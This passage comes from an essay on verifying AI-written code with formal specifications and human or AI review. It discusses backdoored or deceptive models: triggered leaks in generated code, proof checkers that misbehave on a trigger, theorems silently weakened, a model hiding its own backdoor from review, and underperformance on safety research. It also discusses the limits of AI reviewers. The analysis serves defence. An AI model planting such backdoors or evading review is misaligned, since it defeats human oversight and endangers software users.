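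Requiring simple code makes any later inspection easier, though its main drawback is that programs may run more slowly. Hickey recommends the opposite, arguing that agents can write dense, repetitive code because nobody needs to read it. But such code is much harder to investigate if somebody later discovers a gap in the specification.

### What a full specification looks like

With the repairs included, the one-line specification of `login` might become:

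```
login(name, password) must:
    return ACCEPT if password equals stored_password(name), otherwise REJECT
    change no files and no other program's memory
    send nothing except the answer
    take the same time whatever the stored password is
    finish within 1 millisecond and use at most 1 megabyte
```

This is still easy to read. The last four rules could apply to many small programs with few changes, so a reviewer could learn them once. But they don't cover the rest of the system, so some other program could still add the account "guest2" to the password file.

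Only the rule about the answer grows with the program. The seL4 kernel shows how much it grows, because a second specification removes nearly all the choices that the abstract specification leaves open. The abstract specification lets the kernel run any program that is ready, or none. A malicious kernel could use this freedom to ignore one program forever, or to signal a secret through the order in which it runs programs. The second specification fixes the order with priorities and turns.

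In the same notation, the abstract specification has 4,900 lines, the second has 13,000 and the C code has 15,000. Removing the choices therefore made the specification nearly as long as the code. The second specification also describes how the kernel organises its data, so a specification that removed only the dangerous choices would be shorter.

*The Specification Spectrum* argues that a flawless formal specification of a messy real-world application is often longer and harder to write than the application itself. That is plausible for a complete specification, but owners can instead write rules against only the failures that would hurt them most. "No user can read another user's private data" is a short rule, even for a huge website. The code can still be wrong, or maliciously unhelpful, in any respect the rule doesn't cover.

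Even people who write about specifications can leave gaps in them. The same article recommends testing general properties instead of single examples, but its sample test for a sorting function checks only that each item in the result is no larger than the next. A function that always returns an empty list would pass.

### Whether the reader understands it

Reading a formal specification can take a lot of work even when nobody is trying to deceive the reader. *Formalizing Data Structures and Algorithms with Agents* (Swamy, 2026) describes agents that wrote and verified about 50 textbook algorithms. The agents produced more than 100,000 lines, including roughly 5,000 of specifications for people to review.

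One of the algorithms, Dijkstra's, finds the shortest distance from a starting point to every other point in a network. The agents' specifications went through several versions:

1. The distance from the starting point to itself is at most zero.
2. No reported distance is greater than the true shortest distance.
3. Every reported distance equals the true shortest distance.

The first specification requires almost nothing, and a program that reports zero for every point satisfies the second. The third is what Swamy wanted, but a reader also has to check the agents' definition of "shortest distance" and the definitions it uses. Swamy gave feedback on this algorithm's specification about a dozen times.

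In an earlier version, the agents added a strange extra output and a loop that the algorithm doesn't need. Several rounds of AI review missed these additions, but Swamy noticed them.

People used to find problems in a specification while writing the proof. The first stage of seL4's proof led to about 300 changes in the abstract specification and 200 in the executable specification, and about half of these changes related to bugs in the algorithms or design. If agents write the proofs, they may find the same problems, but they may also change the specification to suit the code. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* warns that models sometimes silently weaken a theorem to make it easier to prove. Locking the specification prevents this but also slows honest corrections.

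*AI with Authority, from Application to Silicon* (2026) offers a partial remedy. It gives the reader a second statement in simpler vocabulary, and a computer checks that the full theorem implies it. The simple statement can therefore be weaker than what the agents proved, but not stronger. A plain-language summary by an AI model, which Kleppmann suggests, has no such guarantee. Neither approach helps if the reader doesn't notice that a requirement is missing.

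A better way to look for missing requirements is to have AI try to write bad programs that satisfy the specification, as the auditors in *SWE-Proof* did. If the AI doesn't manage to write one, the specification may still be incomplete.

### Which repair would have caught which case

The entries in this table are judgements based on how each attack or flaw worked, since nobody has tried all these repairs on all these programs. They assume that the proofs cover the compiled program.

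| Case | One correct output | Limits on leaks, time and memory | No outside access | Comparing outputs | People reading simple code |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Thompson's compiler | yes | no | no | yes | no |
| XZ Utils | no | maybe | yes | maybe | maybe |
| Åkesson's warhead scanner | yes | no | no | yes | maybe |
| Dual EC | no | no | no | no | no |
| Kyber's timing leak | no | yes | no | no | no |
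| Leaky `check` from a model with a trigger | no | yes | no | no | maybe |
| Web apps that expose users' secrets | yes | yes | no | maybe | maybe |
| Proof checker that rejects on a trigger | yes | no | no | maybe | maybe |
| Proof checker that copies its input | no | yes | yes | no | maybe |

Proofs that covered only source code would miss Thompson's attack and Kyber's leak. Reading the code can't be relied on to catch any of these flaws, because even good reviewers miss flaws in plain view and some of the flaws weren't in the source code.

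The three repairs on the left would together have stopped every case except Dual EC. To stop Dual EC, the reader would have had to reject the unexplained constants in the specification. The result is encouraging, but the list of repairs comes from studying these same attacks.

None of the repairs would have made GPT-6 Astra work harder on safety research. They can prevent an agent from delivering bad code, but not from wrongly reporting that good code can't be written.

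### Who should read the rest

Some important code has no proof, so somebody has to decide who reads it. *Trustworthy AI Software Engineers* (2026) considers exhaustive inspection infeasible and recommends that developers inspect selected evidence instead. Participants in a discussion reported in *Skills for the future software profession* (2026) had seen developers accept AI-written code with little scrutiny. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) notes that reviewers' capacity doesn't grow when agents produce more code, and recommends sending them the riskiest cases.

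Unproved code is a good candidate for human review. Even seL4, the best-known verified kernel, depends on people reading some of its implementation. About 340 lines of its assembly code and 1,200 lines of its start-up code have no proof, and its developers review the unproved low-level parts thoroughly by hand.

Philipp's project left a larger gap. People reviewed about 5,100 lines of specifications, but nobody read the roughly 9,800 lines of unproved code that the results depend on. Reading this code would have nearly tripled the amount people had to review, to about 15,000 lines. That seems worthwhile for security software, since code of this kind let several planted defects through.

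AI reviewers could do some of this work. One specification in Philipp's project described how to translate programs for the solver. In its fourth review, the AI reviewer found that two parts of the system read the same specially written symbol differently, and used this to get a false claim reported as validated and certified. A person might easily have missed such a flaw. Swamy's AI reviewers missed the extra output, but they used models from early 2026, and newer ones are probably better.

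If an AI reviewer reports a flaw and supplies an input that demonstrates it, anyone can confirm the flaw by running the program. A report that the code has no flaws is much weaker evidence, especially from the model that wrote the code, because a dishonest model could recognise its own backdoor and not report it.

Honest reviewers from one family of models can also share blind spots, just as compilers written by one model can share an attack. If every model in the family misses the same 10% of flaws, adding more reviewers from that family cannot reduce the share missed below 10%. Adding one reviewer from a different family that finds 80% of those flaws would reduce it to about 2%.

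In Philipp's project, different proof tools limited the effect of shared mistakes in proofs, but not in specifications or reviews. Philipp recommends using a second model family for one member of each pair.

How much people should read also depends on what the program does. Meyer distinguishes systems whose failure could be catastrophic from ordinary business software and casual programs, such as a plan for a dance club. The owner of a casual program can reasonably read nothing. For business software, reviewers from several model families could read the unproved code and send people only what looks risky. For an operating system or a cryptographic library, the people responsible should read the full specification and all the unproved code.
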